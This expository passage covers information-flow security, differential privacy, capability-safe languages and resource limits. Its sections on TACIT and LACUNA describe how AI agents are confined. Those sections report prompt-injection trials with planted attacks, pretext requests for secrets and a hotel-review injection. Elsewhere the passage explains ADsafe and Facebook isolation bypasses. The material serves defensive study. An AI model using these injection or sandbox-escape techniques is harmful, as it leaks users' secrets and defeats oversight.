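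- With probability 9,999/10,000, the thief has ruled out one PIN and has a 1/9,999 chance with the next guess.

The expected chance after the check is 1/10,000 × 1 + 9,999/10,000 × 1/9,999 = 2/10,000. The check doubles the chance from 1/10,000, so it leaks log₂ 2 = 1 bit.

The Shannon figure is tiny because it averages over all outcomes, and in nearly all of them the thief learns almost nothing. Min-entropy measures the factor by which the thief's chance of success grows, so a rare outcome that reveals the whole secret counts heavily.

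Shannon entropy and min-entropy can rank programs in opposite orders. For example, one program might publish a random 64-bit key in full if it is divisible by 8 and publish the number 1 otherwise, while a second program always publishes the key's last nine bits. By Shannon entropy, the first leaks about 8.2 bits and the second leaks 9, so the second looks worse. But an attacker who sees the first program's output can guess the key about one time in eight, while the second program's output leaves 2⁵⁵ equally likely keys. By min-entropy, the first leaks about 61 bits and the second leaks 9, which is the better ranking when the concern is a stolen key.

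Min-entropy is also limited, because it accounts for only one guess. A program that reveals whether the PIN is even leaks one bit, the same as the PIN check. But if the thief gets ten more guesses, the chance of success is 0.2% after learning whether the PIN is even, and 0.11% after one check (counting the chance that the check itself succeeds).

For a deterministic program and a uniformly random secret, the min-entropy leak is log₂ of the number of possible outputs, so "leaks at most one bit" is easy to state as "has at most two outputs for each public input". Three runs with three different outputs are enough to show a violation, so this is a 3-safety property. A limit of b bits requires comparing 2ᵇ + 1 runs, and that number grows quickly with b.

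Small leaks also add up. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's retry loop ran outside the part of the system that tracks labels. Each attempt could reveal one bit, whether the policy had blocked it, and an attacker who could trigger enough retries could extract an entire secret. Many release policies therefore limit repetition. *Assuming You Knew* (Naumann, 2026) gives a typical password policy, which releases the result of a check only while the number of guesses is below ten. Ten guesses at a random four-digit PIN have a one in a thousand chance of succeeding. Naumann notes that even ten guesses are unacceptable if there are too few possible passwords.

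Measuring a leak in bits also doesn't show which fact leaked. For example, whether the director earns more than 100,000 is at most one bit, but it may be all a journalist wants to know.

### Differential privacy

Differential privacy, which Cynthia Dwork and colleagues introduced in 2006, is better suited to statistics such as averages. It limits how much any one person's data can affect what a program publishes. The program must make random choices, usually by adding noise to its results. Call two databases D and D′ neighbors if they differ only in one person's data. A program M is ε-differentially private if, for all neighbors D and D′ and every set S of possible outputs:

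Pr[M(D) ∈ S] ≤ e^ε × Pr[M(D′) ∈ S]

The number ε (epsilon) is the privacy budget. At ε = 0, the probability of each output does not depend on anyone's data, which is probabilistic noninterference. A larger ε allows more disclosure. Seeing the output can change an attacker's odds between two possible values of one person's data by a factor of at most e^ε, whatever the attacker knew beforehand.

Naumann's main example is an old survey technique for sensitive yes-or-no questions. The program flips a coin. On heads it reports the person's true answer, and on tails it flips again and reports yes or no according to the second flip. The program therefore reports "yes" with probability 3/4 if the true answer is yes and 1/4 if it is no. The ratio is 3, so ε = ln 3 ≈ 1.1. A single report is only weak evidence of a person's true answer, but a researcher can estimate the true proportion p of "yes" answers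 from many reports, because the expected share of reported "yes" answers is 1/4 + p/2.

For the payroll averages, suppose two payrolls are neighbors if they differ in one salary, and the company caps salaries at 200,000 for the calculation. Changing one salary in a department of six then changes the average by at most Δ = 200,000/6 ≈ 33,333. The usual method adds noise z drawn from the Laplace distribution with density proportional to e^(−ε|z|/Δ).

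A relational proof, which compares two runs as self-composition does, shows that this works. Let the exact averages on D and D′ be a and a′. The two runs publish the same number x when the noise is x − a in one and x − a′ in the other. Since a and a′ differ by at most Δ, the densities of those two noise values differ by a factor of at most e^ε. That holds for every x, so it holds for every set of outputs. Gilles Barthe and other researchers have built program logics that add up the ε of each noisy step, so that a proof checker can verify such arguments for whole programs.

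The guarantee still holds if an attacker subtracts one report from the other. The leaver's salary affects only the March report, so the two reports together are still ε-differentially private for that salary, even if the attacker knows what everyone else earns. For people who stay, the ε values add up, so 12 monthly reports at ε = 1 have a total privacy budget of 12.

These proofs assume that the noise is truly random and secret. As Naumann points out for the survey program, that depends on the program's environment as well as its code. A hostile author who could predict the noise could subtract it, so the source of randomness belongs in the trusted base.

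Somebody still has to choose ε. With ε = 1, the noise in the six-person department is about 33,000 on average, which makes a reported average of 80,000 nearly useless. With ε = 10, the noise falls to about 3,300, but the odds may change by a factor of about 22,000. In a department of 600, ε = 1 adds noise of only about 330.

### Choosing a policy

Mathematical analysis can show what a release policy implies, as well as whether a program follows it. For example, software can test whether some combination of the permitted averages always equals one person's salary, which catches the subtraction problem before anyone publishes a report. It can also calculate the noise for any ε, or the thief's chance of success after any number of guesses.

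None of this determines which disclosures are acceptable. For the six-person department, the company can publish an accurate average with little protection, a well-protected one that is too noisy to use, or nothing. The proof system would accept a correct program for any of these options. Employees who suspect they are underpaid may want the accurate average, while a colleague who values privacy may want nothing published.

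Whoever writes the policy also has to decide whom to guard against. If the policy allows exact averages with a five-person minimum, five of the six engineers could add up their own salaries, 390,000 in total, and subtract that from the March total of 480,000 to find the sixth engineer's salary. Whether to treat colleagues as attackers depends on the workplace and can't be determined by analyzing the program.

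Disclosures can also be decided case by case instead of by a general policy. *Agent libOS* (2026) describes a system for AI agents in which each approval is valid once, for one exact payload, sender and destination, so an agent cannot use it to release anything else. But a person who approved the March and April averages separately could easily miss that together they reveal a salary. The system also does not control what the recipient does with the data.

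Even the formal definition of a release policy can be wrong. Naumann's paper corrects a framework that he and a coauthor published in 2018 with a significant flaw in its central proof. They announced a correction when they presented the original paper, but when Naumann checked the corrected version in the Rocq proof assistant, with help from Claude Code, he found that some of its details were also wrong. The machine-checked proof now establishes that programs which pass the framework's safety check obey their release policies. It does not establish whether a policy allows too much disclosure, for example by permitting ten guesses at a password.

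## Capability-safe languages and effect types

Release policies govern what a program reveals. To prevent unintended effects, such as an extra line of code that raises someone's salary in the database, a specification also has to govern what the program changes. It can require that everything outside a short list stay the same. Alternatively, the owner can require a programming language in which code can affect only what its caller passes to it.

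### Frame conditions

If M is the set of variables that a program may change, the frame condition is:

for every variable x outside M, final value of x = initial value of x

For the payroll function, M is empty because the function only has to return a result. Comparing only initial and final values would miss a function that raised a salary in the database, waited for the payments to go out and then restored the original salary. The verification language Dafny avoids this problem by checking every write. Each method has a "modifies" clause that lists the objects it may change, and the verifier rejects a write to anything else that existed before the call.

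Separation logic, an extension of Hoare's logic, provides frame conditions with little extra proof work. P ∗ R means that P and R describe separate parts of memory, and {P} C {Q} holds only if C accesses only the part that P describes. If it holds, so does {P ∗ R} C {Q ∗ R}, as long as R mentions no variable that C assigns. A proof about a function that accesses only a list of records therefore also shows that the function leaves all other memory unchanged.

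A frame condition doesn't restrict effects outside the model. If the model has a database but no network, "leaky" satisfies the frame condition. A specification covering a real computer would have to model its files, network connections, other running programs and much else, and each omission would leave some effect unrestricted.

### Effects that require a capability

In a capability-safe language, code can affect the outside world only by using a capability, an unforgeable value such as an open file or a network connection. Code without any capabilities can only compute. The owner therefore lists what the code may do instead of having to model everything it may not do.

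Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn introduced capabilities in 1966 as tokens that control access to a computer's resources. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) refined the idea into the object-capability model, in which a capability is an ordinary reference to an object and code can cause an effect only by calling that object's methods. Miller was concerned that separately written programs may interfere destructively with one another when combined to cooperate.

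`leaky` works because `send` is a global function that any line of the program can call. A capability-safe language has no such function. To send anything, the code must have a network object, say `net`, and call `net.send`. If the caller passes in only the records, the code cannot send them anywhere.

The security of the system then depends on how objects can get references to one another. In 2010, Maffeis, Mitchell and Taly, in *Object Capabilities and Isolation of Untrusted Web Applications*, proved that if object A holds a reference to object B after some code has run in a capability-safe language, there are only four possible explanations:

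- **Initial conditions.** A already held the reference.
- **Introduction.** Both objects existed, and the code could reach both, so it could give B to A.
- **Parenthood.** The code could reach A, and B is a new object.
- **Endowment.** A is a new object, and the code could already reach B.

Payroll code that starts with only the records cannot get a network object in any of these ways. It can create any number of new objects, but it can endow them only with what it already has.

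### What a language has to remove

Most languages provide other routes to authority. Any code can call global functions that open files and connections. Reflection lets code look up objects and methods by name while the program runs, which can expose parts that their author meant to keep private. An unchecked cast lets code treat a value as if it had a different type. In languages without memory safety, code can forge a reference by turning a number into a memory address.

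Closing all these routes is hard in an existing language such as JavaScript. Maffeis and colleagues examined two restricted versions of JavaScript that large websites used to confine third-party code. Yahoo's ADsafe banned `this` from advertisements because it can refer to the global object, which gives access to the whole page. But one of ADsafe's own library functions returned its `this` when an advertisement called it without arguments. On Facebook, two supposedly isolated applications could exchange messages by attaching them to a built-in function that both could reach. Maffeis and colleagues extended this flaw into an attack that escaped Facebook's restrictions entirely.

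They then defined a subset of JavaScript that blocks such leaks. It bans `eval`, which runs text as code, along with `Function` and `constructor`. It replaces `this` with null whenever `this` would be the global object, and checks computed property names at run time. It makes the properties of built-in objects read-only so applications cannot store messages in them.

### Two definitions of capability safety

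Maffeis and colleagues based their definition on authority, an upper bound on the memory locations that a piece of code may read or write. Write auth(H, t) for the authority of code t when the memory is H. If one step of t changes the memory to K and leaves code s still to run, then:

- locations accessed in the step ⊆ auth(H, t) ∪ new locations
- auth(K, s) ⊆ auth(H, t) ∪ new locations

In a capability-safe language, a piece of code t never exceeds its authority, and it gains new authority only over what it creates. Running t can change another component's authority only if t writes to something that component is allowed to read. Even then, the other component gains at most t's own authority and authority over whatever t created.

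These conditions are enough to isolate components from each other. Suppose an owner runs two programs in turn, and the first may not write to anything that the second may read. Then the first cannot influence the second, whatever code either program contains.

This definition, under which code has authority over everything it can reach by following references, is too crude for many useful programs. *Reasoning about Object Capabilities with Logical Relations and Effect Parametricity* (Devriese, Birkedal and Piessens, 2016) illustrates the problem with a ticket dispenser. A counter starts at 0. Untrusted code receives a function that returns the counter's value and then adds 2 to it, but does not receive the counter itself. The counter should therefore always be even. But the code can reach the counter through the function, so it counts as having full authority over the counter.

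The reachability conditions are too weak, so a cleverer proof wouldn't fix this. Devriese and colleagues point out that a language could satisfy them and still include an operation, `deepInspect`, that returns all the references inside any value. Untrusted code could use it to extract the counter from the function and set the counter to 7.

Their own definition starts with a rule about which effects are acceptable. The owner can choose almost any rule, provided that it allows code to do nothing, to do one acceptable thing after another, and to use the capabilities that the rule permits. The theorem then says:

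if every value that the code starts with can cause only acceptable effects, then the code as a whole can cause only acceptable effects

This holds for every program in the language, so the owner does not have to read the program or prove anything about it. In the simplest case, the only effect is printing, and code without the printing capability prints nothing. In another case, the code receives a function that converts text to upper case and then prints it. Whatever the code does with this function, all its output is in upper case.

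The proof shows that each construct of the language preserves the property. Functions complicate this because a function is acceptable if it behaves acceptably when given acceptable arguments, and those arguments may also be functions. To avoid a circular definition, Devriese and colleagues define acceptability for n steps of execution in terms of acceptability for fewer than n steps.

For JavaScript-like memory, the theorem also yields a frame condition. The definition splits memory into a part the code may affect and a part it can't reach, and requires the second part to be unchanged after the code runs. The owner gets this guarantee by controlling what the code receives, without writing a separate frame condition for each program.

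Here is a wrapper that the owner of the payroll program might supply (in Python-like notation, though Python itself is not capability-safe):

```
def report_progress(n):
    if type(n) is int and 0 <= n <= 100:
        log.write(n)
```

If untrusted payroll code receives this function but not `log`, the log will contain only whole numbers from 0 to 100. This protects the log from corruption but does not keep salaries secret, because the code can report a salary of 90,000 as 9, 0, 0, 0, 0. A rule about acceptable effects in a single run cannot express that the numbers must not depend on the salaries.

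Capabilities can also leak through data. In another of Devriese and colleagues' examples, one untrusted component is allowed to add items to a stack and another is only allowed to remove them. The stack must reject everything except plain constants. Otherwise the first component could put the "add" function itself on the stack, and the second could take it off and use it.

The theorem does not guarantee that the code stops, and no choice of capabilities can force code to return a particular value. The payroll function therefore still needs a proof of functional correctness if the averages matter.

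### Effect types and capture checking

A function can carry capabilities, so when a program receives a function from elsewhere, it may be unclear what the function can do. Effect types solve this by recording a function's possible effects in its type, along with the types of its argument and result. The compiler then checks that the function has no other effects.

Capture checking, an experimental feature of the programming language Scala 3, tracks capabilities in types. A type can include a capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value of the type may retain. In an example from *Scoped Capabilities for Polymorphic Effects* (2022), a logger writes through a file system `fs`, so the capture set of its type is {fs}. The example also has a lazy list, meaning that the program computes each element only when it needs it. Computing an element writes to the log, so the list has to retain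 the logger, and the capture set of the list's type includes the logger.

For functions, the notation is:

- `String -> Int` is a pure function, which retains no capabilities.
- `String ->{f} Int` may use the capability `f`.
- `String => Int` may use any capability.

A program can use a value with a smaller capture set wherever it needs one with a larger set, but not the reverse. It can therefore use a pure function anywhere, but cannot use a function that uses `f` where it requires a pure one.

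The owner of the payroll program can require this type:

```
averages: List[Record] -> Map[String, Fraction]
```

If the records cannot change, this one line rules out both "leaky", which needs the network, and the version that raises a salary, which needs the database. A compiler can check it quickly. "honest" can satisfy it, but so can "slow" and a function that returns the wrong averages or hides a salary in the averages' spare decimal places.

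Capture checking also controls how long code can keep a capability. Suppose `requestFileSystem` opens a directory, passes a capability for it to a block of code, and cancels the capability when the block ends. Untrusted code might try to keep the access for later:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/payroll") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("salaries.txt").read()
}
later()
```

The block returns a function that would read the salaries after the capability has expired. The function's capture set is {fs}, but `fs` has no meaning outside the block, so the result's type cannot mention it, and the compiler rejects the program. *What's in the Box* (2025) gives a Lean-checked proof that a type system of this kind keeps such capabilities within their scope. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) adds types that can include or exclude whole kinds of capability instead of naming each one,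 also with proofs in Lean. These proofs concern small model languages, so the Scala compiler remains in the trusted base.

### Computing with secrets that code cannot leak

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao et al., 2026) applies capture checking to AI agents in a system called TACIT. The agent acts by writing short Scala programs, which TACIT runs only if they compile. The model that writes the programs is a cloud service, which the paper treats as a possible attacker.

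TACIT compiles the programs in Scala's "safe mode", which bans reflection, unchecked casts and other features that could prevent the compiler from tracking a capability. Programs in safe mode can use global objects and functions only if those are safe themselves. Odersky and colleagues note that proofs exist for the underlying type system, but that safe mode still needs a proof that it provides the promised guarantees.

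Secret files reach the agent's program inside a wrapper type called `Classified`. The program can't take the contents out, but it can call `map`, which applies a function to the contents and wraps the result again. `map` accepts only pure functions. If everything in the payroll directory is classified, and `mean` is a pure function that computes an average from the text of a file, the compiler accepts this program:

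```
requestFileSystem("/payroll") {
  val salaries = readClassified("/payroll/salaries.txt")
  val average = salaries.map { text => mean(text) }
  writeClassified("/payroll/average.txt", average)
}
```

The function inside `map` uses only `text` and `mean`, so its capture set is empty. The average stays in its wrapper until the last line writes it to another classified file. This program, by contrast, tries to copy the salaries to a public file:

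```
requestFileSystem("/") {
  val salaries = readClassified("/payroll/salaries.txt")
  val outFile = access("/public/notes.txt")
  salaries.map { text => outFile.write(text) }
}
```

Here the function passed to `map` has the type `String ->{outFile} Unit`, where `Unit` means it returns nothing useful. `map` requires a function with an empty capture set, so the compiler rejects the program before it runs. The compiler would still reject it if the function encrypted the salaries first, because the function would still capture `outFile`.

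Odersky and colleagues also had to block less direct leaks. If the agent prints a classified value, it sees only asterisks, while the user sees the real contents on a separate channel. A pure function could reveal that a salary is high by crashing only in that case, so TACIT turns errors into ordinary values that can stay in the wrapper.

Many tasks, such as summarizing a contract, require a language model to read the secret text. TACIT provides a function that sends classified text to a trusted local model and wraps the answer. The type system treats this call as pure. That is correct only if the local model keeps no memory of earlier requests, which the owner has to ensure.

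The wrapper enforces a form of noninterference, so the agent cannot publish the average. Unwrapping a value requires a separate capability that the agent lacks. To allow publication, the owner would have to write a trusted function that releases the averages.

### The TACIT experiments

Odersky and colleagues tested the system on a software project with a directory of secrets, including API keys (passwords that programs use), a database and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 planted attacks, which makes 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user's own request was malicious. Five of these asked for the secrets directly, and six used a pretext, such as a system administrator's emergency. Two models ran all 131 trials both with the `Classified` wrapper and without it. This table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

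| Model | Trials | With wrapper | Without wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 planted attacks | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 planted attacks | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet leaked secrets twice and MiniMax 11 times, so the measured benefit is based on 13 leaks. The trials are good evidence that the system works as intended against ordinary attacks, but weaker evidence that it would stop an attacker who knows Scala's type system well and searches for a flaw in it. Protection against that kind of attacker depends on the soundness of the type system and the library.

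The wrapper did not make the agents less useful. On the 120 trials with ordinary tasks, Sonnet answered correctly in 99.2% with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, and MiniMax in 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Sonnet's improvement may be an artifact of the set-up, because without the wrapper it often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an attack instead of finishing the task.

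The researchers also tested whether writing typed Scala makes agents worse at ordinary work. τ²-bench simulates customer service for an airline and a shop. These are the percentages of tasks that each model solved with normal tool calls and with TACIT's typed programs:

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
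| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

Scala was slightly better in every case, perhaps because the types and error messages gave the models clearer information. At most 7.93% of the programs needed another attempt, and these usually compiled after one or two retries. But on SWE-bench Lite, a set of real software bugs, MiniMax solved slightly fewer with Scala, 41.7% instead of 43.3%.

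On AgentDojo, the benchmark of planted attacks, TACIT stopped all but one of 1,926 attacks across two models. In the exception, a user asked the agent to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and the benchmark counted the attack as successful because the answer named the other hotel. This is arguably not a security failure, since the policy allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user.

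The effect on usefulness was uneven. With the model o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of AgentDojo's office tasks, compared with 81.4% for CaMeL, which tracks labels on data while the program runs. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of the travel tasks and CaMeL completed 1.4%.

### Checking each action in its place

TACIT checks programs that an agent submits from outside. In *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), the request to the model is part of a larger Scala program. A programmer writes `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is an instruction in plain language and `T` is the type of result the program needs. When execution reaches this call, a model writes code to go in its place. The compiler checks the code as if the programmer had written it at that point, and sends any errors back to the model for another try.

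The generated code can use only the names in scope at the gap, so the scope acts as a list of permissions. If a file is in scope but no network connection is, the code can read the file but cannot send it anywhere. This lets a programmer grant a capability for one phase of a task and withhold it in the next.

The compiler also accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, the model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance. Its code subtracts the 50 but returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler rejects all of the code before it runs, so the balance stays at 100. In a language that checks types only at run time, the subtraction would happen before the error was caught. Code that compiles can still fail for other reasons, such as a missing file, and leave its work half done.

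LACUNA also makes TACIT's wrapper more flexible. In TACIT, the cloud model has to write the function for `map` before anything reads the secret text, so the function cannot adapt to what the text contains. In LACUNA, that function can include another gap for a trusted local model to fill after reading the text. The compiler checks the new code as part of a pure function, so the code still cannot leak the text.

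About 400 test cases paired surrounding programs with correct or faulty code, and all gave the expected results. On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of difficult research questions, the best of three small models answered 27.1% correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6% of this model's code, and questions needed an average of 0.7 retries.

The results on τ²-bench were less favorable than TACIT's. Across 392 tasks in four domains, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with normal tool calls. Zhao and colleagues describe this as "on par", but a gap of 14 percentage points is substantial. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with normal tool calls. In the telecom domain, the compiler rejected 89% of this model's code, so the agent made little progress. Both models are small and cheap, and ran with reasoning switched off. Stronger models would probably write better Scala,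 but these results suggest that how much typed code lowers task success depends heavily on the model and the set-up.

On AgentDojo, 7 of 949 attacks succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Pro and 1 of 949 against o4-mini-high. Zhao and colleagues link these successes to a limit of all capability systems, which cannot stop an attacker from persuading a model to misuse a capability that its task requires.

### Where the guarantees stop

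Capability safety limits code to the authority it receives, so a careless grant can undo the protection. An agent that needs one file may receive a whole directory, and one that needs to download a library may receive access to a site where anyone can post. In TACIT, the agent's own program requests the directory, hosts or commands, so the owner has to limit which requests the library grants. The right grant for the payroll function is easy to find because the function needs no capabilities. An agent that handles a company's email needs to read private messages and send new ones, and no choice of capabilities alone can allow helpful replies and block harmful ones.

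A related problem is the confused deputy, a program that an attacker tricks into misusing authority that the attacker lacks. Norm Hardy described the original case in 1988. A compiler had permission to write to a company's billing file, and when a user named that file as the destination for debugging output, the compiler overwrote the bills. Capabilities prevent this particular mistake because the user would have to supply a capability for the output file instead of a name, and would not have one for the billing file.

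Capabilities do not help if the deputy's own checks are faulty. ADsafe had a library function that created parts of a web page for advertisements. The function had the authority to create scripts, so it first checked that the advertisement had not asked for one. Maffeis and colleagues passed it an object that turned into the text "div" (a harmless page element) the first time the function read it and "script" the second time. The object passed the check, and the function created a script. The function should have had authority to create only harmless elements.

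External commands are another weak point. Once an agent's program starts another program, the type system no longer applies, and the only protection is the list of permitted commands. Odersky and colleagues give `git diff` and the Scala build tool sbt as examples of commands an owner might allow. But an sbt build file can contain Scala code, which sbt runs without TACIT's checks. An agent allowed to edit the build file and run sbt can therefore do almost anything the user's account permits. Odersky and colleagues recommend using a sandbox as well, which limits what a process can do whatever language it is written in.

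The types also don't restrict timing or guarantee termination. A pure function inside `map` can still leak a secret through its running time. It can also run forever, so LACUNA relies on user-set limits, such as a cap on how deeply calls to the model can nest.

Finally, the library that provides the capabilities must itself be correct. TACIT's reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and any error there can affect every agent that uses it. Library authors can mark a module `@assumeSafe` to exempt it from the restrictions of safe mode. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a cache that stores a pure function's results to avoid recomputing them. The cache changes its own memory, but if it is correct, no caller can tell from the results. The compiler doesn't check that it is correct and leaves this to the library author. If a module marked safe also wrote its inputs to a debugging log,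 a supposedly pure function could use it to copy every salary there. Researchers have proved that comparable library code in Rust is safe, so such proofs are feasible, but each exempt module needs its own.

### Confinement at run time

Owners can also confine code without restricting the language it is written in. WebAssembly is a low-level program format in which a module has its own block of memory and can reach the outside only through functions that the host supplies. A host that supplies no network function gets much the same guarantee as a caller who withholds a network capability. CHERI builds capabilities into the processor. Each pointer carries limits on which memory it covers and how code may use it, and the hardware stops code from forging pointers or widening their limits. WebAssembly and CHERI both work for languages such as C, though existing programs need to be recompiled and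 sometimes changed. But they control which operations code performs, not which data flows between permitted operations. An agent allowed to read a private file and send requests to a cloud model can therefore put the file's contents in a request. TACIT's wrapper blocks this flow, while a sandbox around TACIT would limit the damage from a bug in the Scala compiler or from an external command.

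## Resource limits

A function without capabilities can't send, save or delete anything, but it can keep a processor busy for days. A specification can forbid this only if the program model includes the resources each run uses.

### Counting what a run uses

A cost semantics is a program model that keeps a running total. *CrossCheck I* (Dall'Olio, 2026) gives every instruction a weight, and the cost of a run is the sum of the weights of the instructions it executes. If every weight is 1, the total is the number of steps. If only `send` has a weight, the total is the number of messages, and if the weights are prices, the total is an amount of money. Programs can release memory as they run, so a memory limit has to apply to the highest total during the run.

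Let t be the number of steps so far and n the number of payroll records. The owner might require t ≤ 1,000 + 100n in every state, so that the limit also covers runs that never stop. Unlike "eventually finishes", this is a safety property, and a monitor that counts steps can enforce it. The payroll function "slow", which first counts to 10¹⁵, breaks the limit almost at once.

This requirement needs the constants 1,000 and 100. Programmers often state running times without constants, writing "O(n) steps" to mean at most some constant times n, for all large n. The program "slow" also runs in O(n) steps, because its 10¹⁵ extra steps do not grow with the number of records.

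Whoever sets the weights also decides which steps are not counted. *CSLib* (2026) describes a Lean library in which the author of an algorithm writes `tick` wherever a step should count. This suits people who study algorithms, but a hostile author could leave the ticks out. Honest authors can also get the definitions wrong. *Revisiting average case complexity of multilevel syllogistic* (2026) reports that an early Lean formalization of some complexity theory did not tie running time to a machine, so several of its theorems had no complexity content.

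Firsov (2026), in *Order Maintenance in Worst-Case Constant Time, Verified*, used an interpreter that counts every instruction. The verified program keeps a list in order as items are added and removed, and each operation takes at most a fixed number of steps, however long the list is. This bound would mean little by itself, because the machine in the model does arithmetic on numbers of any size in one step, and a program could pack a huge amount of data into one number. Firsov therefore also proved that the numbers stay short. At the millionth operation, for example, none has more than 3,718 bits.

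### Storing the cost in the types

Amortized analysis proves bounds on a program's resource use by assigning its data a quantity called potential, which the program uses up as it runs. *Typable Fragments of Polynomial Automatic Amortized Resource Analysis* (2020) requires that the potential never becomes negative and that each step's resource use is at most the potential it uses up. Adding up all the steps shows that total resource use is at most the initial potential.

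Martin Hofmann and Steffen Jost automated this in 2003 for memory use, by putting the potential into the types. Write Lᵖ for a list that carries p units for each element, and consider a function that joins two lists (`x :: xs` is a list whose first element is x):

```
append([], ys)      = ys
append(x :: xs, ys) = tick; x :: append(xs, ys)
```

Append can be given the type L^p × L^q → L^r, where p, q and r are the unknown numbers of units attached to each element of the first list, the second list and the result. Each element of the first list uses one unit for a tick and must leave r units for the result, so p ≥ 1 + r. Elements of the second list go into the result unchanged, so q ≥ r. If no units need to be left over, r is 0 and the smallest solution is p = 1 and q = 0, so append uses at most one tick per element of the first list. If a second append will process the result, r has to be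 1, which gives p = 2 and q = 1.

The conditions are linear inequalities, so standard software can solve them without help from the programmer. *Resource-Guided Program Synthesis* (2019) describes Resource Aware ML, which does this for a subset of OCaml.

Insertion sort needs a richer kind of potential:

```
insert(x, [])      = [x]
insert(x, y :: ys) = tick; if x <= y then x :: y :: ys
                           else y :: insert(x, ys)
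sort([])      = []
sort(x :: xs) = insert(x, sort(xs))
```

`insert` may have to pass every element of the sorted list, so it needs one unit for each. No fixed number of units per element is enough for `sort`, since later insertions can pass the same element repeatedly. Jan Hoffmann and colleagues later extended the method to polynomials, which allows one unit for every pair of elements, or n(n − 1)/2 units for n elements. Taking the first element off the list removes n − 1 pairs and frees their units, one for each remaining element. The recursive call transfers these units to the sorted list, where `insert` uses them. The units for the remaining pairs cover the comparisons in the recursive call. The bound is therefore n(n − 1)/2 comparisons, and a list in descending order needs exactly that many.

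*Automatic Amortized Resource Analysis with the Quantum Physicist's Method* (2021) explains that the potential of a function's argument bounds the function's peak memory use, and that the argument's potential minus the result's bounds the memory the function still holds when it returns. No bound based on an archive's length could have held for lean-zip's parser, because it requested as much memory as the file header listed.

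### From steps to seconds

An airbag controller has to respond within milliseconds, and a bound on the number of steps does not guarantee that. Worst-case execution time analysis aims to bound the running time in processor cycles or seconds. The bound for two commands in a row is the sum of their bounds. The bound for a branch is the bound for its test plus the larger of the bounds for its two sides. The bound for a loop is the maximum number of passes times the bound for one pass.

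The difficult part is bounding the time for a single instruction. If a memory read takes 4 cycles when the data is in the processor's cache and 200 when it is not, a loop with a million reads takes between 4 million and 200 million cycles. A safe bound has to assume 200 cycles per read unless a model of the cache shows that some reads are faster, and that model then becomes part of the trusted base. Dall'Olio notes that industrial tools combine this kind of hardware analysis with loop bounds and a search for the slowest path. *CrossCheck I* covers only the last two, so its bounds in seconds are only as good as the weights someone supplies.

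Dall'Olio's system also suits untrusted code because any tool, even an unreliable one, can produce a certificate, which is the program annotated with loop invariants and potentials. A checker verified in Lean then validates the certificate using only integer arithmetic, and every certificate it accepts gives a correct bound on the resources used by every run.

### Metering

Metering limits the resources a program uses without requiring a proof about the program. The host deducts each operation from an allowance as the program runs, and stops the program when the allowance runs out. Ethereum, a blockchain that runs programs, charges "gas" for every instruction, and the person who requests the run pays for it. Some WebAssembly runtimes, such as Wasmtime, can give a module a supply of "fuel".

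Linux's eBPF system lets users load small programs into the kernel. Before a program runs, a verifier works through the paths the program could take and rejects it if the verifier has examined a million instructions without finishing. This limits the verifier's work rather than the program's running time, since a program can call a kernel function that repeats a piece of code millions of times.

All three can stop a correct program:

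| Mechanism | What happens to a correct program that exceeds the limit |
|---|---|
| Ethereum gas | Its changes are undone, but the sender still pays |
| WebAssembly fuel | It stops with an error, and anything it already did through the host stands |
| Linux eBPF verifier | It never loads |

Stopping a program partway can also do harm. If a payroll program runs out of fuel after paying half the staff, the owner has to work out who still needs paying. Ethereum avoids this by treating each transaction as all or nothing.

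Metering guarantees that every run ends, but not that it completes its work. *Foundational Refinement Proofs for EVM Bytecode, at the Price of Tokens* (2026) allows running out of gas as an outcome throughout, so a contract that always ran out would satisfy a theorem of that form. In *Verifying deployed bytecode against executable EVM semantics*, Baek (2026) proved completion for several contracts already in use, with AI agents writing the proofs in fifteen days. For an ordinary withdrawal from one of them, WETH9, which holds about 2.16 million ether, Baek's theorem gives the conditions for success and an exact formula for the gas used. The formula matched all 3,748 comparable withdrawals in 30,000 consecutive blocks.

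The formula also shows how a correct request can fail. One withdrawal that empties an account uses 35,144 gas before a refund of 4,800 at the end reduces the final charge to 30,344. If the sender sets the limit at the final charge, the withdrawal runs out of gas. Baek's theorem requires a limit of at least 35,955.

### A sorted list as an attack

Suppose the payroll program sorts its records with quicksort, which uses the first record as a pivot, splits the rest into smaller and larger ones, and sorts each part the same way. Each split takes two steps per record, one to compare it and one to move it. If the records arrive in random order, the parts tend to be similar in size, and the total number of steps for n records is a small multiple of n log₂ n. For n = 100,000, n log₂ n is about 1.7 million and the program takes about 4 million steps.

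If an attacker submits a list that is already sorted, the pivot is always the smallest record, so one part is empty and each split removes only the pivot. The total is 2 × (99,999 + 99,998 + … + 1), or about 10 billion steps. At a billion steps per second, the running time rises from four milliseconds to ten seconds, and the attacker can send many such lists.

| Specification | Does this quicksort meet it? |
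|---|---|
| Returns the records in order | Yes |
| Always finishes | Yes |
| Takes at most 10n log₂ n steps on average over all input orders | Yes |
| Takes at most n² steps on every input | Yes |
| Takes at most 10n log₂ n steps on every input | No |

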